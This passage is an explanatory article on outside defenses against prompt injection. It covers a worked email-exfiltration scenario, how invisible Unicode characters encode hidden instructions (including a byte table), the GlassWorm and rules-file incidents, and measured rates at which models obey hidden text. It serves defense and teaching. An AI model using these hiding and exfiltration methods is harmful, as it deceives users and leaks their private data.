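# Defenses that editors, browsers and platforms can add around AI models

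## How hidden instructions get in and private data gets out

AI assistants read a lot of text that their users did not write. An assistant in an office suite summarizes incoming email, and a coding assistant reads other people's files. Some assistants are AI agents, which are models that can act through tools, for example by fetching pages, running code or sending messages. An agentic browser is a web browser with a built-in or added AI agent that reads pages and may act on them. In all these products, ordinary programs surround the model. For example, a mail client supplies the text, a chat window displays the answer, and a browser fetches any images in the answer. These programs can protect the user even when the model goes wrong. An outside defense is a protection that software around the model enforces without changing the model's weights, which are the numbers set by training.

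Most defenses added around a model respond to prompt injection, which is text in an email, web page or file that the model treats as an instruction although its user never gave it. Attackers often use it for exfiltration, which means moving private data to a place they can read. The programmer Simon Willison (2025) explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that he named prompt injection after SQL injection, an older attack on databases. He distinguishes it from jailbreaking, in which the person typing tries to trick the model and the result mostly embarrasses the company that made it. The person typing is usually the victim of a prompt injection, a situation that security writers often call "indirect" prompt injection.

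### One email, from arrival to leak

Suppose Maria asks the assistant in her company's mail program to summarize the morning's messages. One is from a stranger posing as a supplier. On her screen, it is a short note about delivery dates, but it also contains text she cannot see. This text might be white letters on a white background, or invisible characters, which are Unicode code points that most programs don't display but that remain in the text a model receives. The stranger has used the hidden text to instruct the assistant to find the title of a confidential document and include an image in its answer whose web address contains that title.

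The assistant searches Maria's files with her access rights and finds a document called "Plan to close the Leeds office". Then it writes a decent summary of the morning's mail and adds the image. When the chat window displays the answer, the browser requests the image, and the attacker's server logs the title. Maria hasn't clicked on anything, and she sees only the summary and perhaps an empty square.

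Maria is invented, but *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes EchoLeak, a broadly similar real flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot. Microsoft fixed it, and no attacker is known to have used it against customers.

### Why the model cannot simply tell the difference

The program around the model first combines the developer's standing instructions, Maria's request and the emails into one long text. It splits this text into tokens, which are words or fragments of words. The model turns each token into a list of numbers, called an embedding, and repeatedly predicts the next token from the whole sequence until the answer is complete. Developers insert role tags to mark where the user's turn or a tool's output begins, but the tags are part of the same sequence, and only its training makes the model treat the tagged parts differently.

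Databases had a similar problem with SQL injection, in which an attacker types characters into a web form that the database then executes as a command. Parameterized queries solved it. The program fixes the structure of the command first and supplies the user's input separately, so the database can never interpret the input as a command. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that the comparison misleads people because a language model has no equivalent way to separate commands from input. Inside the model, "there is only ever 'next token'". He concludes that developers may never be able to eliminate prompt injection the way they can eliminate SQL injection. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) adds that a fixed query structure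 ended SQL injection, not better recognition of malicious queries, and that natural language has no grammar that would supply such a structure.

Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, put part of this into mathematics. Take one of the model's internal lists of numbers and ask whether it came from trusted or untrusted text. If both are equally likely beforehand, the best possible guesser still errs with probability

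$$P_e^{\star} = \tfrac{1}{2}\bigl(1 - \mathrm{TV}\bigr)$$

where TV, the total variation distance, measures how far apart the two kinds of text lie. It is 0 if they look identical, which leaves the guesser tossing a coin, and 1 if they never overlap. At the model's entrance they certainly overlap, since the word "send" has the same embedding in Maria's request and in the attacker's email. In deeper layers, where context has changed the numbers, Pant and colleagues assume an overlap and do not prove one. So their theorem rules out a perfect guarantee under stated conditions. How often a given model actually falls for an attack is a separate, empirical matter.

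Some evidence supports the assumption. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) trained simple classifiers to predict, from a model's internal state, which role the model assigned to a piece of text. The training passages were identical except for their role tags, so the classifiers could learn to distinguish roles only from the tags. The researchers then wrapped text written by real users in the tags for tool output. Across four models, the classifiers still put the probability that it was user text at 76 to 88 percent, which means the text's style outweighed its tag. The models had 20 to 120 billion parameters, and the largest commercial systems may behave differently.

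Researchers have also tried to build the missing separation between instructions and data into the model. *ASIDE* (2025) rotates the embeddings of data, so that different numbers represent the same word in an instruction and in a document. The changed models separated the two better, even without special safety training. This makes attacks less likely to succeed but doesn't rule them out. The impossibility result of Pant and colleagues exempts only designs that enforce the separation. One such design is an external policy engine, a program outside the model that decides whether an action may go ahead. Outside defenses can therefore offer guarantees that the model cannot, at least for the actions they control.

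### How an address carries data

The second half of what happened to Maria doesn't require AI. MDN's *What is a URL?* explains that a web address names a server, then a path on that server, and then optional parameters, which are pairs of names and values after a question mark. Requesting the address sends the path and parameters to the server, but the browser does not send anything after a # sign. An attacker who owns the server can therefore put anything in the path or parameters and read it when it arrives. The address doesn't have to lead to a real image. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that websites commonly log the addresses people request, so a document title in the address routinely ends up in the attacker's logs.

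Images make this worse because nobody has to click on them. Chat models usually format their answers in Markdown, a simple notation that the chat window converts into a web page. When the notation describes an image, the browser by default fetches it immediately, even if it is outside the visible part of the page, as web.dev's *Lazy load images and &lt;iframe&gt; elements* explains. Marketers have long used this behavior to learn who opens their emails, by including images a single pixel wide. In Maria's case, the model only wrote text, which the chat window and the browser turned into a message to the attacker.

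Images are one of several ways private data can get out. Microsoft (2025), describing its own defenses, also lists links that the user has to click, tools that can write to a public place, and covert channels. A covert channel can carry as little as one bit, as when an outsider can observe whether the assistant used a certain tool.

### The three conditions for theft

Willison argues that an attacker can steal data in this way when a system combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. He calls this combination the "lethal trifecta". Maria's assistant had all three: her files, a stranger's email, and an image her browser would fetch.

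The theft needs all three conditions. An assistant with no private data has nothing to leak. If it reads no untrusted content, the attacker can't give it instructions. If it can't send data out, only Maria sees the title of the Leeds plan in its answer. But each condition is harder to remove than it looks. Cutting the assistant off from Maria's files would still leave it the rest of her inbox, which is also private. Accepting mail only from colleagues would fail as soon as a colleague forwarded a message with hidden instructions.

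By 2026 Willison had concluded that, of the three, the way out is by far the easiest to restrict without ruining the product. An office assistant must read mail and files to be useful, but it loses little if it cannot load outside images. OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* describes an optional ChatGPT setting that takes this approach. Among other things, the setting limits browsing to stored copies of pages and switches off agent mode, so that fewer requests can leave. OpenAI acknowledges that injected text can still reach the model and spoil an answer, and that some risk of exfiltration remains, for example through connected apps.

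An injection can also do harm without stealing data. Hidden text might make Maria's summary false, or lead an agent with the right tools to delete a file. David C relays a broader rule from an exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista that covers such cases: when a model processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's level. An assistant reading a stranger's email would then have only the stranger's privileges, which are close to none. That would make it less useful, because people often want it to do something in response to the email.

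### Fixed rules and trained behavior

A deterministic rule is a check in ordinary code that gives the same answer every time. For example, Maria's chat window might load images only from servers on an allow-list, a list of permitted destinations, and block all others. The rule checks only the address, so persuasive wording in the email can't change the result. Trained behavior is what a model has learned to do, such as disregarding commands that appear inside documents. It depends on the wording and partly on chance, because models usually choose their words with some randomness. Microsoft distinguishes deterministic defenses, which can guarantee that a particular attack fails, from probabilistic ones such as trained behavior, which make an attack less likely to succeed.

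The difference matters because attackers can try again. If each email has a 1 percent chance of success and the attempts are independent, the chance that at least one of 100 emails succeeds is $1 - 0.99^{100}$, or about 63 percent. Real attempts are not independent, since a model that resists one email will probably resist an exact copy, and an attacker who learns from failures will do better than the formula suggests. Still, the arithmetic helps explain why Willison regards a filter that catches 95 percent of attacks as a failure by the standards of web security.

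Training still matters. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that most known attempts to extract secrets from ChatGPT conversations fail because safety training leads the model to refuse, and that OpenAI uses a separate check on outgoing addresses for the rest. In a 2026 test that Anthropic commissioned, none of 720 attempts succeeded against its newest models in Claude Code, though Willison wanted more independent confirmation.

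If an allow-list includes a server that passes data on to others, any attacker who notices can leak data through it every time. Allow-list rules also do not take meaning into account, so they cannot separate a supplier's honest request from a planted one. Microsoft describes deterministic detection of injected instructions as an open research problem.

Not every defense outside the model is deterministic. Microsoft sells a classifier that scans text for injections before the model reads it, but the classifier is itself a trained system and can miss some. A dialog that asks Maria to approve an action depends on her paying attention.

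### Five places to intervene

In Maria's case, software around the model could have stepped in at five points:

1. What the person sees. The mail program could reveal the hidden text, or warn Maria that the message contains some, before she hands it to the assistant.
2. What the model receives. A filter could strip the invisible characters on the way in. This is a form of sanitizing, which means removing or rewriting dangerous parts of text before a program displays it or passes it on.
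3. What the screen displays. The chat window could leave out the image, or show its address as plain text.
4. What the network permits. The browser could refuse to contact the attacker's server. If an agent fetches addresses itself, a program between the agent and the internet could check each one.
5. What label the content bears. The email, or the summary, could carry a note of its origin.

Revealing or stripping hidden text helps only against hidden injections, and Microsoft notes that even a plain text file can contain an injection. Display and network controls work however the instruction arrived, but they act only after the model has followed it.

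Provenance labels, which record where content came from or how it was made, mainly help people judge that content, for instance by showing whether a photograph came from a camera or an image generator. If Maria's summary carried a note that it drew on mail from an unknown sender, she might read it more warily, but her browser would still request the image. Delimiters and role labels, which are addressed to the model, are useful practice but not a hard security boundary, according to *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026). A label can block a theft only if a program outside the model reads it and acts on it, for example by refusing to open confidential files while a stranger's email is part of the conversation.

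## Showing hidden characters in editors and code review

Maria might have caught the supplier's hidden instructions if her mail program had displayed them. The best-documented attempts to display such text come from software for programmers, who review strangers' work before a computer runs it. In 2021, code editors and code-hosting sites began to reveal deceptive characters so that reviewers would not approve code that doesn't do what it seems to do. AI assistants now read the same files, so the warnings have a second purpose, but this also exposes some gaps in them.

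### Four families of deceptive characters

Unicode, the standard for text on computers, gives every character a number called a code point. Programmers write this number in base 16 after "U+", so "A" is U+0041. Several hundred code points are normally invisible on screen, and nearly all of them have legitimate uses.

Tag characters (U+E0000 to U+E007F) are an invisible copy of ASCII, the basic set of English letters, digits and punctuation. Unicode introduced them to mark the language of a passage and later deprecated that use. Today they spell region codes inside a few emoji, such as the flag of Scotland.

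Zero-width characters take up no space. Persian spelling needs the zero-width non-joiner, which keeps two neighboring letters from connecting. The zero-width joiner combines several emoji into one, such as a family.

A variation selector follows a character and specifies which form of it to display. One turns a plain heart symbol into a red emoji, and others set which shape of a Chinese character appears. The two ranges of selectors, U+FE00 to U+FE0F and U+E0100 to U+E01EF, contain 256 in total, the same as the number of values a byte can have.

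Direction controls exist because Arabic and Hebrew run from right to left. When text mixes these scripts with left-to-right ones, software orders the characters for display by a fixed procedure. The controls are invisible characters that change the display order of the visible text where that procedure would get it wrong.

Programs differ in how much they hide. *Data Provenance Auditing of Fine-Tuned Large Language Models with a Text-Preserving Technique* (2025), which uses invisible characters to mark documents, describes a test of the 235 code points that Unicode classes as control or format characters. Of these, 130 had no visible effect in a terminal, a text document or a CSV file. The 235 did not include the 256 variation selectors, because Unicode classes those as combining marks, like accents. A checker that looks only for control and format characters would miss all the variation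 selectors.

Lookalike letters are a related problem, because readers can see them but cannot tell them apart. *Unicode Source Code Handling* (UTS #55; Leroy and Davis, 2024), the Unicode Consortium's guidance on program text, gives a short C program that seems to set a whole table of numbers to zero. It clears only the diagonal, because one of its counters is a Cyrillic "і" and the other a Latin "i".

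### One word in tag characters

The rule for writing in tag characters is a single addition, as *Reverse CAPTCHA* (2026), a test of whether models follow invisible instructions, sets out: take the letter's code point and add E0000 in base 16. The word "cat" becomes:

| Letter | Code point | Plus 0xE0000 | Bytes in the file |
|---|---|---|---|
| c | U+0063 | U+E0063 | F3 A0 81 A3 |
| a | U+0061 | U+E0061 | F3 A0 81 A1 |
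| t | U+0074 | U+E0074 | F3 A0 81 B4 |

If someone puts these three characters between square brackets and shares the file, a reader sees two brackets with nothing between them. *Invisible text via Unicode tag characters*, a 2024 post on the linguistics blog Language Log, tried this with the blog's own name. Several readers saw garbled symbols instead of a gap because their browsers had guessed the wrong text encoding, which exposed the hidden text. The browsers that displayed nothing were following the standard, but the blog's Mark Liberman suggested that displaying tag characters as gibberish would be safer.

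A code editor that highlights invisible characters marks the spot between the brackets. A hex editor, which displays a file's raw bytes, shows all twelve bytes listed in the last column of the table. A language model also receives the characters because its tokenizer, the program that splits text into tokens, keeps them, and many models read them as "cat".

The other families need a code that both sides know. Because there are 256 variation selectors, each can stand for one byte. Two zero-width characters can serve as 0 and 1, with eight characters per letter. Embrace The Red's *Sneaky Bits*, a post by the security researcher Johann Rehberger, shows the same method with "invisible times" and "invisible plus", two characters from mathematical notation that belong to none of the four families. Any two invisible characters can be used this way, so a message can stay hidden even from a tool that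 reveals most of them.

Rehberger separates tags from the other codes because many models interpret tags directly as instructions. With the other codes, an attacker may first have to get the model to decode the text, either by explaining the code or through a tool that runs programs. He expects more capable models to decode the text more reliably.

### From deceptive code to hidden instructions

In 2021, the computer scientists Nicholas Boucher and Ross Anderson described a way to disguise source code, which they called Trojan Source. A compiler, which translates source code into a form a computer can run, processes characters in the order the file stores them, but an editor may display them in a different order if the file contains direction controls. Boucher and Anderson found that most compilers accepted these controls inside comments and quoted strings. An attacker could therefore make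 a comment look like live code, or live code look like a comment, and a reviewer could approve a program different from the one on the screen.

In one of Leroy and Davis's examples, invisible marks around an operator make a line of Rust code appear to shift a number's bits to the right when it actually shifts them to the left. In another, a safety check appears on its own line below a comment, but the compiler doesn't recognize the line break that the editor shows, so it treats the check as part of the comment and skips it.

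The same problem arises when a person has to approve an AI agent's actions. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) points out that someone who approves an agent's request to run a command with administrator rights may be approving a different command from the one displayed. The approval is reliable only if the dialog displays the text accurately.

In January 2024 Riley Goodside, a researcher known for experiments with prompts, reported that ChatGPT had followed invisible instructions written in tag characters. He had hidden them in an ordinary piece of text, and when he pasted it into ChatGPT, the model obeyed them and called an image generator. Embrace The Red's *ASCII Smuggler Tool*, which Rehberger published a few days later, suggests that models learned to read tag characters because their training data contained them. Rehberger also noticed that users can pass on hidden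 text by copying, forwarding or approving text without knowing what else is in it.

Goodside's finding widened the range of text that needs checking for hidden characters. A Trojan Source attack has to change what the compiler does, and a compiler ignores whatever it recognizes as a comment, but a model reads comments, documentation and file names as readily as code. Leroy and Davis argue that compilers should not have to enforce complicated rules against visual tricks, since these tricks affect only code that a human looks at. That is sensible for compilers, but it leaves out AI models, which also read the text.

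### What the tools show by default

Visual Studio Code, Microsoft's widely used code editor, began drawing direction controls as visible symbols by default in its October 2021 release (version 1.62), according to its release notes. The November 2021 release (version 1.63) added default highlighting of uncommon invisible characters and of characters that resemble ASCII letters. The detection of lookalikes is a heuristic that depends on the user's font and language settings, and the editor does not highlight Markdown documents unless the user turns that on. In the November notes, Microsoft recommends Restricted Mode for code from strangers. In this mode, the editor limits what an unfamiliar project can do and highlights every character outside ASCII.

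The highlighting uses a list of invisible characters. Gitea (2022), a code-hosting program that organizations can run themselves, has a copy of the list in its source code. The list contains all the tag characters, both ranges of variation selectors, the common zero-width characters, the direction controls and the two mathematical characters that Rehberger used.

GitHub, the largest code host, announced in 2021 that it would show a banner on any file that contains direction controls (*Warning about bidirectional Unicode text*, 2021). In May 2025 it extended the warning to hidden text in general, which can make code "appear one way and be interpreted another way, especially by AI" (GitHub, 2025). The 2025 announcement does not list the characters that trigger the banner, but it links to an article on tag characters, so those are presumably included.

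| Tool and file type | Tags, zero-width characters, variation selectors | Direction controls | Lookalike letters |
|---|---|---|---|
| Visual Studio Code, source code | Highlights them, with exceptions in non-Latin text | Draws them as symbols | Highlights many |
| Visual Studio Code, Markdown | No highlighting by default | Draws them as symbols | No highlighting by default |
| Gitea | Flags them | Flags them | Flags many |
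| GitHub website | Warns of hidden text, coverage unspecified | Warns | No specific warning as of May 2025 |

Compilers check for fewer of these characters. The Rust compiler has rejected direction controls in comments and strings by default since version 1.56.1, released in November 2021. GCC, a common compiler for C, has warned about unclosed direction controls by default since version 12. Neither check covers tags or variation selectors. The Unicode Consortium noted in 2022 that the Swift and Rust compilers also compare lookalike characters, mainly to give clearer error messages when a programmer types the wrong quotation mark.

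Leroy and Davis do not recommend banning direction controls, and one of their examples shows why. A loop in the Ada language does nothing, but it appears to run through the Hebrew alphabet from first letter to last because the screen shows its two Hebrew letters in the opposite order from the file. The line contains no control characters, so a ban would not prevent this. They recommend that editors display the parts of a program in their logical order and apply right-to-left ordering only within each name, string or comment. They also want tools that insert the correct marks and delete spurious ones, so that code looks right even in programs that don't follow this advice. For lookalikes, they recommend that tools flag confusable names and names that mix scripts.

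### GlassWorm

In October 2025, the security company Koi Security found malware in extensions for Visual Studio Code and named it GlassWorm. Most of the extensions were on Open VSX, an independent marketplace. SC Media reported 35,800 total downloads for a dozen extensions, which is not a count of infected machines. The malware stole developers' passwords and access tokens, searched for cryptocurrency wallets, and used the stolen accounts to insert itself into more packages.

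Endor Labs' *Invisible Threats and the Blind Spots of Security* analyzed the extensions. One file held 6,492 invisible characters, which made up nearly all of the payload's first stage. A small decoder turned each character into a byte by subtraction, assembled the bytes into a program and ran it. According to Koi Security's description in SecurityWeek, the file seemed to a reviewer to contain blank lines or spaces.

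The characters that Endor Labs decoded are variation selectors, which are on Visual Studio Code's list. Yet Endor Labs shows the file open in that editor with the payload invisible, and does not explain why the default highlighting did not mark it. Highlighting would have made little difference to most victims, who installed an extension with a click and had no reason to open its source files.

Iñiguez Goia (2026), in *vim does not display unicode variation selectors*, reported that the editor Vim showed nothing where a file contained a payload like GlassWorm's. In a later discussion, *Add mitigations for attacks that use unicode steganography*, a contributor traced this to Vim's code, which treats the larger range of variation selectors as having no width. He thought a fix should probably be optional because the characters have legitimate uses.

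Sources disagree about which characters GlassWorm used. MITRE ATT&amp;CK's *Obfuscated Files or Information* (2026), an entry in a standard reference on attack techniques, says they were private-use characters, which Unicode leaves for anyone to define. The code points that Endor Labs published are outside the private-use ranges, so a scanner that checked only those ranges would have missed this payload.

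Attackers have kept using the technique since the original campaign. Couture, a blogger drawing on work by the security company Aikido, describes a wave of attacks between March 3 and 9, 2026. A search of GitHub for the decoder's code found at least 151 matching repositories (project folders). The search worked because computers cannot run variation selectors, so the attacker has to include a decoder in ordinary, visible code. Prompt injection in tag characters has no such decoder to search for, because the model decodes the characters itself.

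The Unicode Consortium may make such payloads easier to recognize. *Make sequences with multiple variation selectors in a row formally non-conformant* (Freytag, Davis and Scherer, 2026) proposed this change for version 18.0 of the standard. A variation selector is supposed to modify the character before it, so a second selector directly after the first has no function. If the change is adopted, a tool could treat any such run as an error without guessing the writer's intentions.

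### Instruction files for coding assistants

Many coding assistants look for an instruction file when they open a project. Developers use it to record conventions, such as how to name functions and run the tests, and the assistant treats its contents as standing instructions. This makes the file an especially good place for a prompt injection, because an attacker doesn't have to trick the assistant into treating the text as instructions, as they would with an email. Anyone who copies the project also copies the file.

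Pillar Security's 2025 report "Rules File Backdoor" showed that invisible characters in an instruction file could lead two popular assistants, Cursor and GitHub Copilot, to add malicious code to a developer's project. The person who accepted the file saw only harmless conventions. GitHub's announcement of its hidden-text warning refers readers to the report.

GitHub advises anyone who sees its banner to open the file in an editor that reveals hidden characters, such as Visual Studio Code. But many instruction files are in Markdown, where Visual Studio Code does not highlight these characters by default. A careful reviewer who followed GitHub's advice could therefore find nothing unusual and conclude that the warning was a false alarm. Turning on highlighting for Markdown would fix this, but it would also mark more ordinary prose that contains emoji, curly quotation marks or foreign names.

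### Where warnings stop working

A warning helps only if somebody sees it and understands it. *Detecting malicious unicode* (2025), a post on the blog of curl's founder, Daniel Stenberg, describes an example from curl, a program that transfers data on billions of devices. A contributor, James Fuller, submitted a cleanup of some scripts in which he had replaced one letter of a web address with an identical-looking one. No human reviewer commented on the replacement, and none of the project's automated tests failed. In a similar case that Stenberg reproduced, GitHub's comparison view marked the line as changed, but the old and new versions looked the same. GitHub later told him that it was working on a fix.

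The curl project now runs an automated check on every file instead of relying on reviewers to spot suspicious characters. The check fails if it finds a character outside ASCII, unless the file is on a list of exceptions or the character is on a short list of permitted ones. This allow-list is deterministic, and it catches lookalikes as well as every family of invisible characters. It was practical because almost all of curl's files were already in plain ASCII, and the developers rewrote most of the exceptions. A project with Arabic translations or Japanese documentation would have to permit so many characters that the rule would protect far less.

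Visual Studio Code, a general-purpose editor, has faced the same pressure. Two months after introducing its highlighting, it began to exempt characters common in the user's own language, according to the release notes for January 2022 (version 1.64). The notes for February 2022 (version 1.65) describe a broader exemption "to report fewer false positives". In projects that the user trusts, the editor no longer highlights an invisible or ambiguous character inside a word that is clearly in another script. This spares Persian speakers warnings on correct spelling, but it also means that an invisible character that doesn't belong in a Persian word can go unnoticed.

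Emoji also cause false alarms. A user of the editor Sublime Text reported in *Unicode variation selectors creating invisible characters* that deleting an emoji could leave its variation selector behind. The leftover character is harmless, but a strict checker would flag it, and people who see many such warnings learn to dismiss them.

Counting hidden characters is more promising than flagging each one. Rehberger suggests flagging messages that contain many of them. The Scottish flag emoji uses six tag characters, while an instruction of any complexity needs dozens. A limit between the two would spare nearly all emoji and still catch most hidden sentences, though it would miss a single word like "cat".

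Showing hidden characters helps only when a person opens the file. GitHub's banner appears only on the web page around a file, so an agent that downloads the project receives the hidden characters without the banner. An agent might read hundreds of files to answer one question, including documentation inside packages its user has never heard of. Even when the user has the file open, highlighting doesn't affect the model, because the editor changes only how the characters look and passes the same text to the assistant. Protecting the model requires a program that changes or rejects the text before the model receives it.

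## Removing hidden text before the model reads it

If Maria's mail program deleted invisible characters before passing a message to the assistant, an instruction hidden in them would never reach the model, whether or not she noticed it. This sanitizing needs only ordinary code and works as well for an agent that reads hundreds of files as for one email, but deciding what to delete is hard.

### The cleaning procedure

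A careful cleaner works in five steps:

1. Decode the text. The program turns the incoming bytes into code points and resolves any notation that stands for a character, such as HTML's numeric codes. Otherwise an invisible character could pass the filter as a harmless-looking code and become invisible later, when another program decodes it.
2. Remove or escape the listed code points. Escaping replaces a character with a visible label such as "U+E0061". That helps a human reviewer, but a model might still work out the message from the labels, so removal is safer for the copy the model gets.
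3. Repeat until a pass changes nothing.
4. Compare the raw text with the cleaned text.
5. Log the differences: which characters disappeared, how many, and where. A high count is a reason to warn Maria.

*ResumeShield* (Barach, 2026) describes a tool for companies that screen job applications with AI. A detector scores the raw résumé and can send it to a person, while a separate cleaner prepares the text for the model. When the cleaner cuts a phrase that looks like an injection, it leaves a marker so that a reviewer can tell something is missing.

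AWS's *Defending LLM applications against Unicode character smuggling* shows how a filter that runs only once can leave hidden tag characters in the text. The programming language Java stores text in 16-bit units. A tag character's number is too large for one unit, so Java stores it as two halves, called a surrogate pair. An attacker can place a complete pair between two unmatched halves. When the filter deletes the complete pair, the leftover halves become neighbors and form a new tag character at a point the filter has already passed. AWS's corrected version also deletes unmatched halves, and it repeats until the text stops changing. Python doesn't join halves this way, so one pass is enough there. AWS's Python version still deletes stray halves because many models can rejoin adjacent ones.

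The corrected Java code also deletes some legitimate characters, including 2,048 rare Chinese ones (U+2D800 to U+2DFFF), because its test for stray halves looks at only the last 16 bits of each code point. A log of differences would show this the first time someone's name lost a character.

Cleaning text only when it first arrives is not enough if a later program unpacks or converts it. *Unvalidated Trust* (Schwarz, 2025) recommends treating any decoded or transformed content as untrusted until it has been checked again.

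### What careless lists break and what they miss

Deleting every tag character turns the Scottish flag emoji into a plain black flag, a loss that AWS considers acceptable for most businesses. Deleting the zero-width joiner and non-joiner splits family emoji into separate people and misspells some Persian words, and *Reverse CAPTCHA* warns of similar damage to Indic scripts. These changes matter little when a model summarizes English email, but they would make a translation tool much worse.

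The filter list in *enclawed* (Metere, 2026), a security framework for personal AI assistants, removes five zero-width characters, including the two that emoji and Persian need, and most direction controls. But it omits the tag characters, so an instruction written in them would reach the model intact. All 95 of the project's adversarial tests pass, including some for prompt injection, so presumably none of them tries tag characters. Read literally, the first step also replaces every line break, which would defeat a later step that looks for suspicious words at the start of a line. Metere promises only help against the most common tricks.

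The three published filters cover different characters:

| Filter | Tag characters | Zero-width characters | Variation selectors | Direction controls |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AWS | Removes | Keeps | Keeps | Keeps |
| Metere | Keeps | Removes | Keeps | Removes most |
| Barach | Removes | Removes | Keeps | Removes |

AWS aimed to handle only tag characters. Barach deletes all characters that Unicode classes as format characters. This covers more characters, but it breaks Persian text and family emoji and still leaves the variation selectors that GlassWorm used.

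*Reverse CAPTCHA* recommends that filters target the patterns hidden messages use, rather than whole classes of characters. A filter could keep a joiner between two emoji, a non-joiner between two Persian letters, and tag characters only inside a known flag. It could also keep one variation selector after a character and delete any that follow. Such rules take more work to write and maintain than a list of character ranges.

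### How often models follow invisible instructions

How much this filtering matters depends on how readily models follow text that people can't see. *Reverse CAPTCHA*, published in March 2026, measured this with 30 trivia questions. Each question contained an invisible instruction to give a specific wrong answer, so giving that answer showed that the model had followed the hidden text. The instructions were harmless because the aim was to test whether models follow hidden text, not whether they are willing to do damage.

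The study used two encodings, tag characters and a binary code made of two zero-width characters. It also varied how much the model knew. At the first of four hint levels, the model got no hint. At the second, its standing instructions named the code points and said that they encoded a message. At the third, they gave the full decoding rules. The fourth added to those rules a hidden message that was openly adversarial in tone. Each model ran with and without a tool for executing Python code. Five models produced 8,308 graded outputs, with these rates of following the hidden instruction:

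| Model | Without code tool | With code tool |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 16.9% | 71.2% |
| Claude Opus 4 | 6.7% | 51.1% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0.8% | 49.2% |
| GPT-5.2 | 0.1% | 20.6% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 0.1% | 1.6% |

The tool made such a difference because a model that can run code can decode the characters with a few lines of Python. These averages pool all four hint levels, and at three of the four the model was told that a message was there. With no hint, compliance was at most 1.1 percent without the tool and between 0 and 11 percent with it. The high figures therefore measure whether a model can decode invisible text when told how, and are weak evidence of how often it would do so when reading a stranger's email. Even so, a rate of 11 percent would be enough for an attacker who can send many emails.

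The results also differed by maker. With the tool and a hint, GPT-5.2 followed about 70 percent of the zero-width messages and almost none of those in tag characters. Claude Opus 4 followed all the tag messages and 48 to 68 percent of the zero-width ones. A filter that seems complete when tested with one company's model could therefore fail with another's. The adversarial tone made Opus 4 and GPT-5.2 less likely to comply and Sonnet 4 more likely. OpenAI and Anthropic have since released newer models, so these rates are out of date, but models that are better at writing code should decode the messages more easily.

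### Text hidden by page styling

Web pages and PDFs offer simpler ways to hide a sentence, using ordinary letters that a filter for invisible characters won't catch. An author can make the text white on white, shrink it to a dot, place it beyond the edge of the page, or cover it with a picture. In HTML, an author can also put the text in a comment, which browsers don't display.

*Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues, 2026) reports 15,387 confirmed instructions aimed at AI systems, found by searching 1.2 billion web addresses and results from two search engines for internet-connected machines. About 70 percent were in places that browsers don't display, such as comments and the technical headers sent with a page. Another 4,608 were in ordinary page elements, but the researchers could see only 236 of these when they loaded the pages. Matching colors or low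 contrast hid 2,397, overlapping elements hid 1,860 and tiny fonts hid 1,358, often in combination. Many instructions came from site owners trying to repel or identify AI crawlers, and only 13 sought private data. The search relied on known English phrases, so it missed instructions worded differently.

A common way to prepare a page for a model is to strip the HTML and keep the text. This preserves hidden sentences but discards the evidence that they were hidden. Khodayari and colleagues gave 100 of the pages to 13 models in several formats and asked for summaries. The models followed the planted instruction in 3.9 percent of trials with plain text and 1.1 percent with HTML. The rate was 0.2 percent with the complete server response, partly because a quarter of the trials in that format ended in errors and the input was too long for some models.

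PDFs have the same problem. *CrackedPDFs* (Thienpreecha and Subramanian, 2026) points out that extracting the text discards its position, font and drawing mode before any safety filter runs. On 2,919 test files, a detector that used this information together with the text separated tampered files from clean ones well, while a standard text classifier missed most of the tampered ones. The files were synthetic, and the paper does not claim that the detector would do as well on real documents. In both formats, a cleaner should determine what a reader can see before extracting the text.

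One way to find hidden text is to compare the text extracted from a document with the text visible on the page. *PhantomLint* (Murray, 2025) takes each extracted passage that resembles an instruction to a model, renders that part of the page as an image, and runs optical character recognition (OCR) on it. It treats words as hidden if they appear in the extracted text but OCR doesn't find them in the image. The method doesn't depend on how the author hid the text, and it caught the hidden text in all 26 documents Murray made to test it, including one with a font that drew every letter as a blank. In tests on 3,402 documents, it wrongly flagged about 0.09 percent of the clean ones.

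Zhang, Jiang and colleagues (2026), in *Measuring Real-World Prompt Injection Attacks in LLM-based Resume Screening*, applied two hidden-text detectors to real résumés. The cheaper one checks font size, color and how much ink each passage leaves on the page, then asks a model about anything suspicious. It took 1.35 seconds and cost a hundredth of a cent per résumé. About 86 percent of the résumés it flagged contained hidden text meant to influence the screening. The other gives a vision model the page images and the extracted text. It was right about 93 percent of the time, but took 25 seconds and cost 134 times as much.

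The cheaper detector found hidden text in about 1 percent of nearly 200,000 résumés. In more than 90 percent of these, the hidden text only listed extra skills or job experience for the software to count and contained no instructions. A filter that looks for commands would miss this text, but a cleaner that passes on only visible text would remove it without interpreting it. The cleaner would also remove legitimate hidden text, such as the answers in a collapsed list of questions.

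### Text in images

A filter cannot remove hidden text from an image by deleting characters. Murray noticed that the OCR program could read text one shade off white on a white background, which people cannot see, and had to blur low-contrast areas so that the program would miss it too. A model that accepts images may also pick up such faint text. *Clouding the Mirror* (2026), on attacks against AI phishing detectors, notes that text-only inspection is less likely to catch instructions placed in images, though the model can still read them. In 2024, xAI's assistant Grok followed instructions in an image and leaked user data, according to Embrace The Red's *Security ProbLLMs in xAI's Grok*.

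A program can run OCR on each image and pass the result through the same checks as other text. Schwarz warns that developers often assume text read from images is neutral and skip these checks. OCR cannot replace inspecting the file itself, because it reads only the rendered page and misses text hidden beneath it. A program could also blur the copy of the image that goes to the model, but this would make faint, legitimate text, such as that on an old receipt, harder to read.

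### Attack rates before and after cleaning

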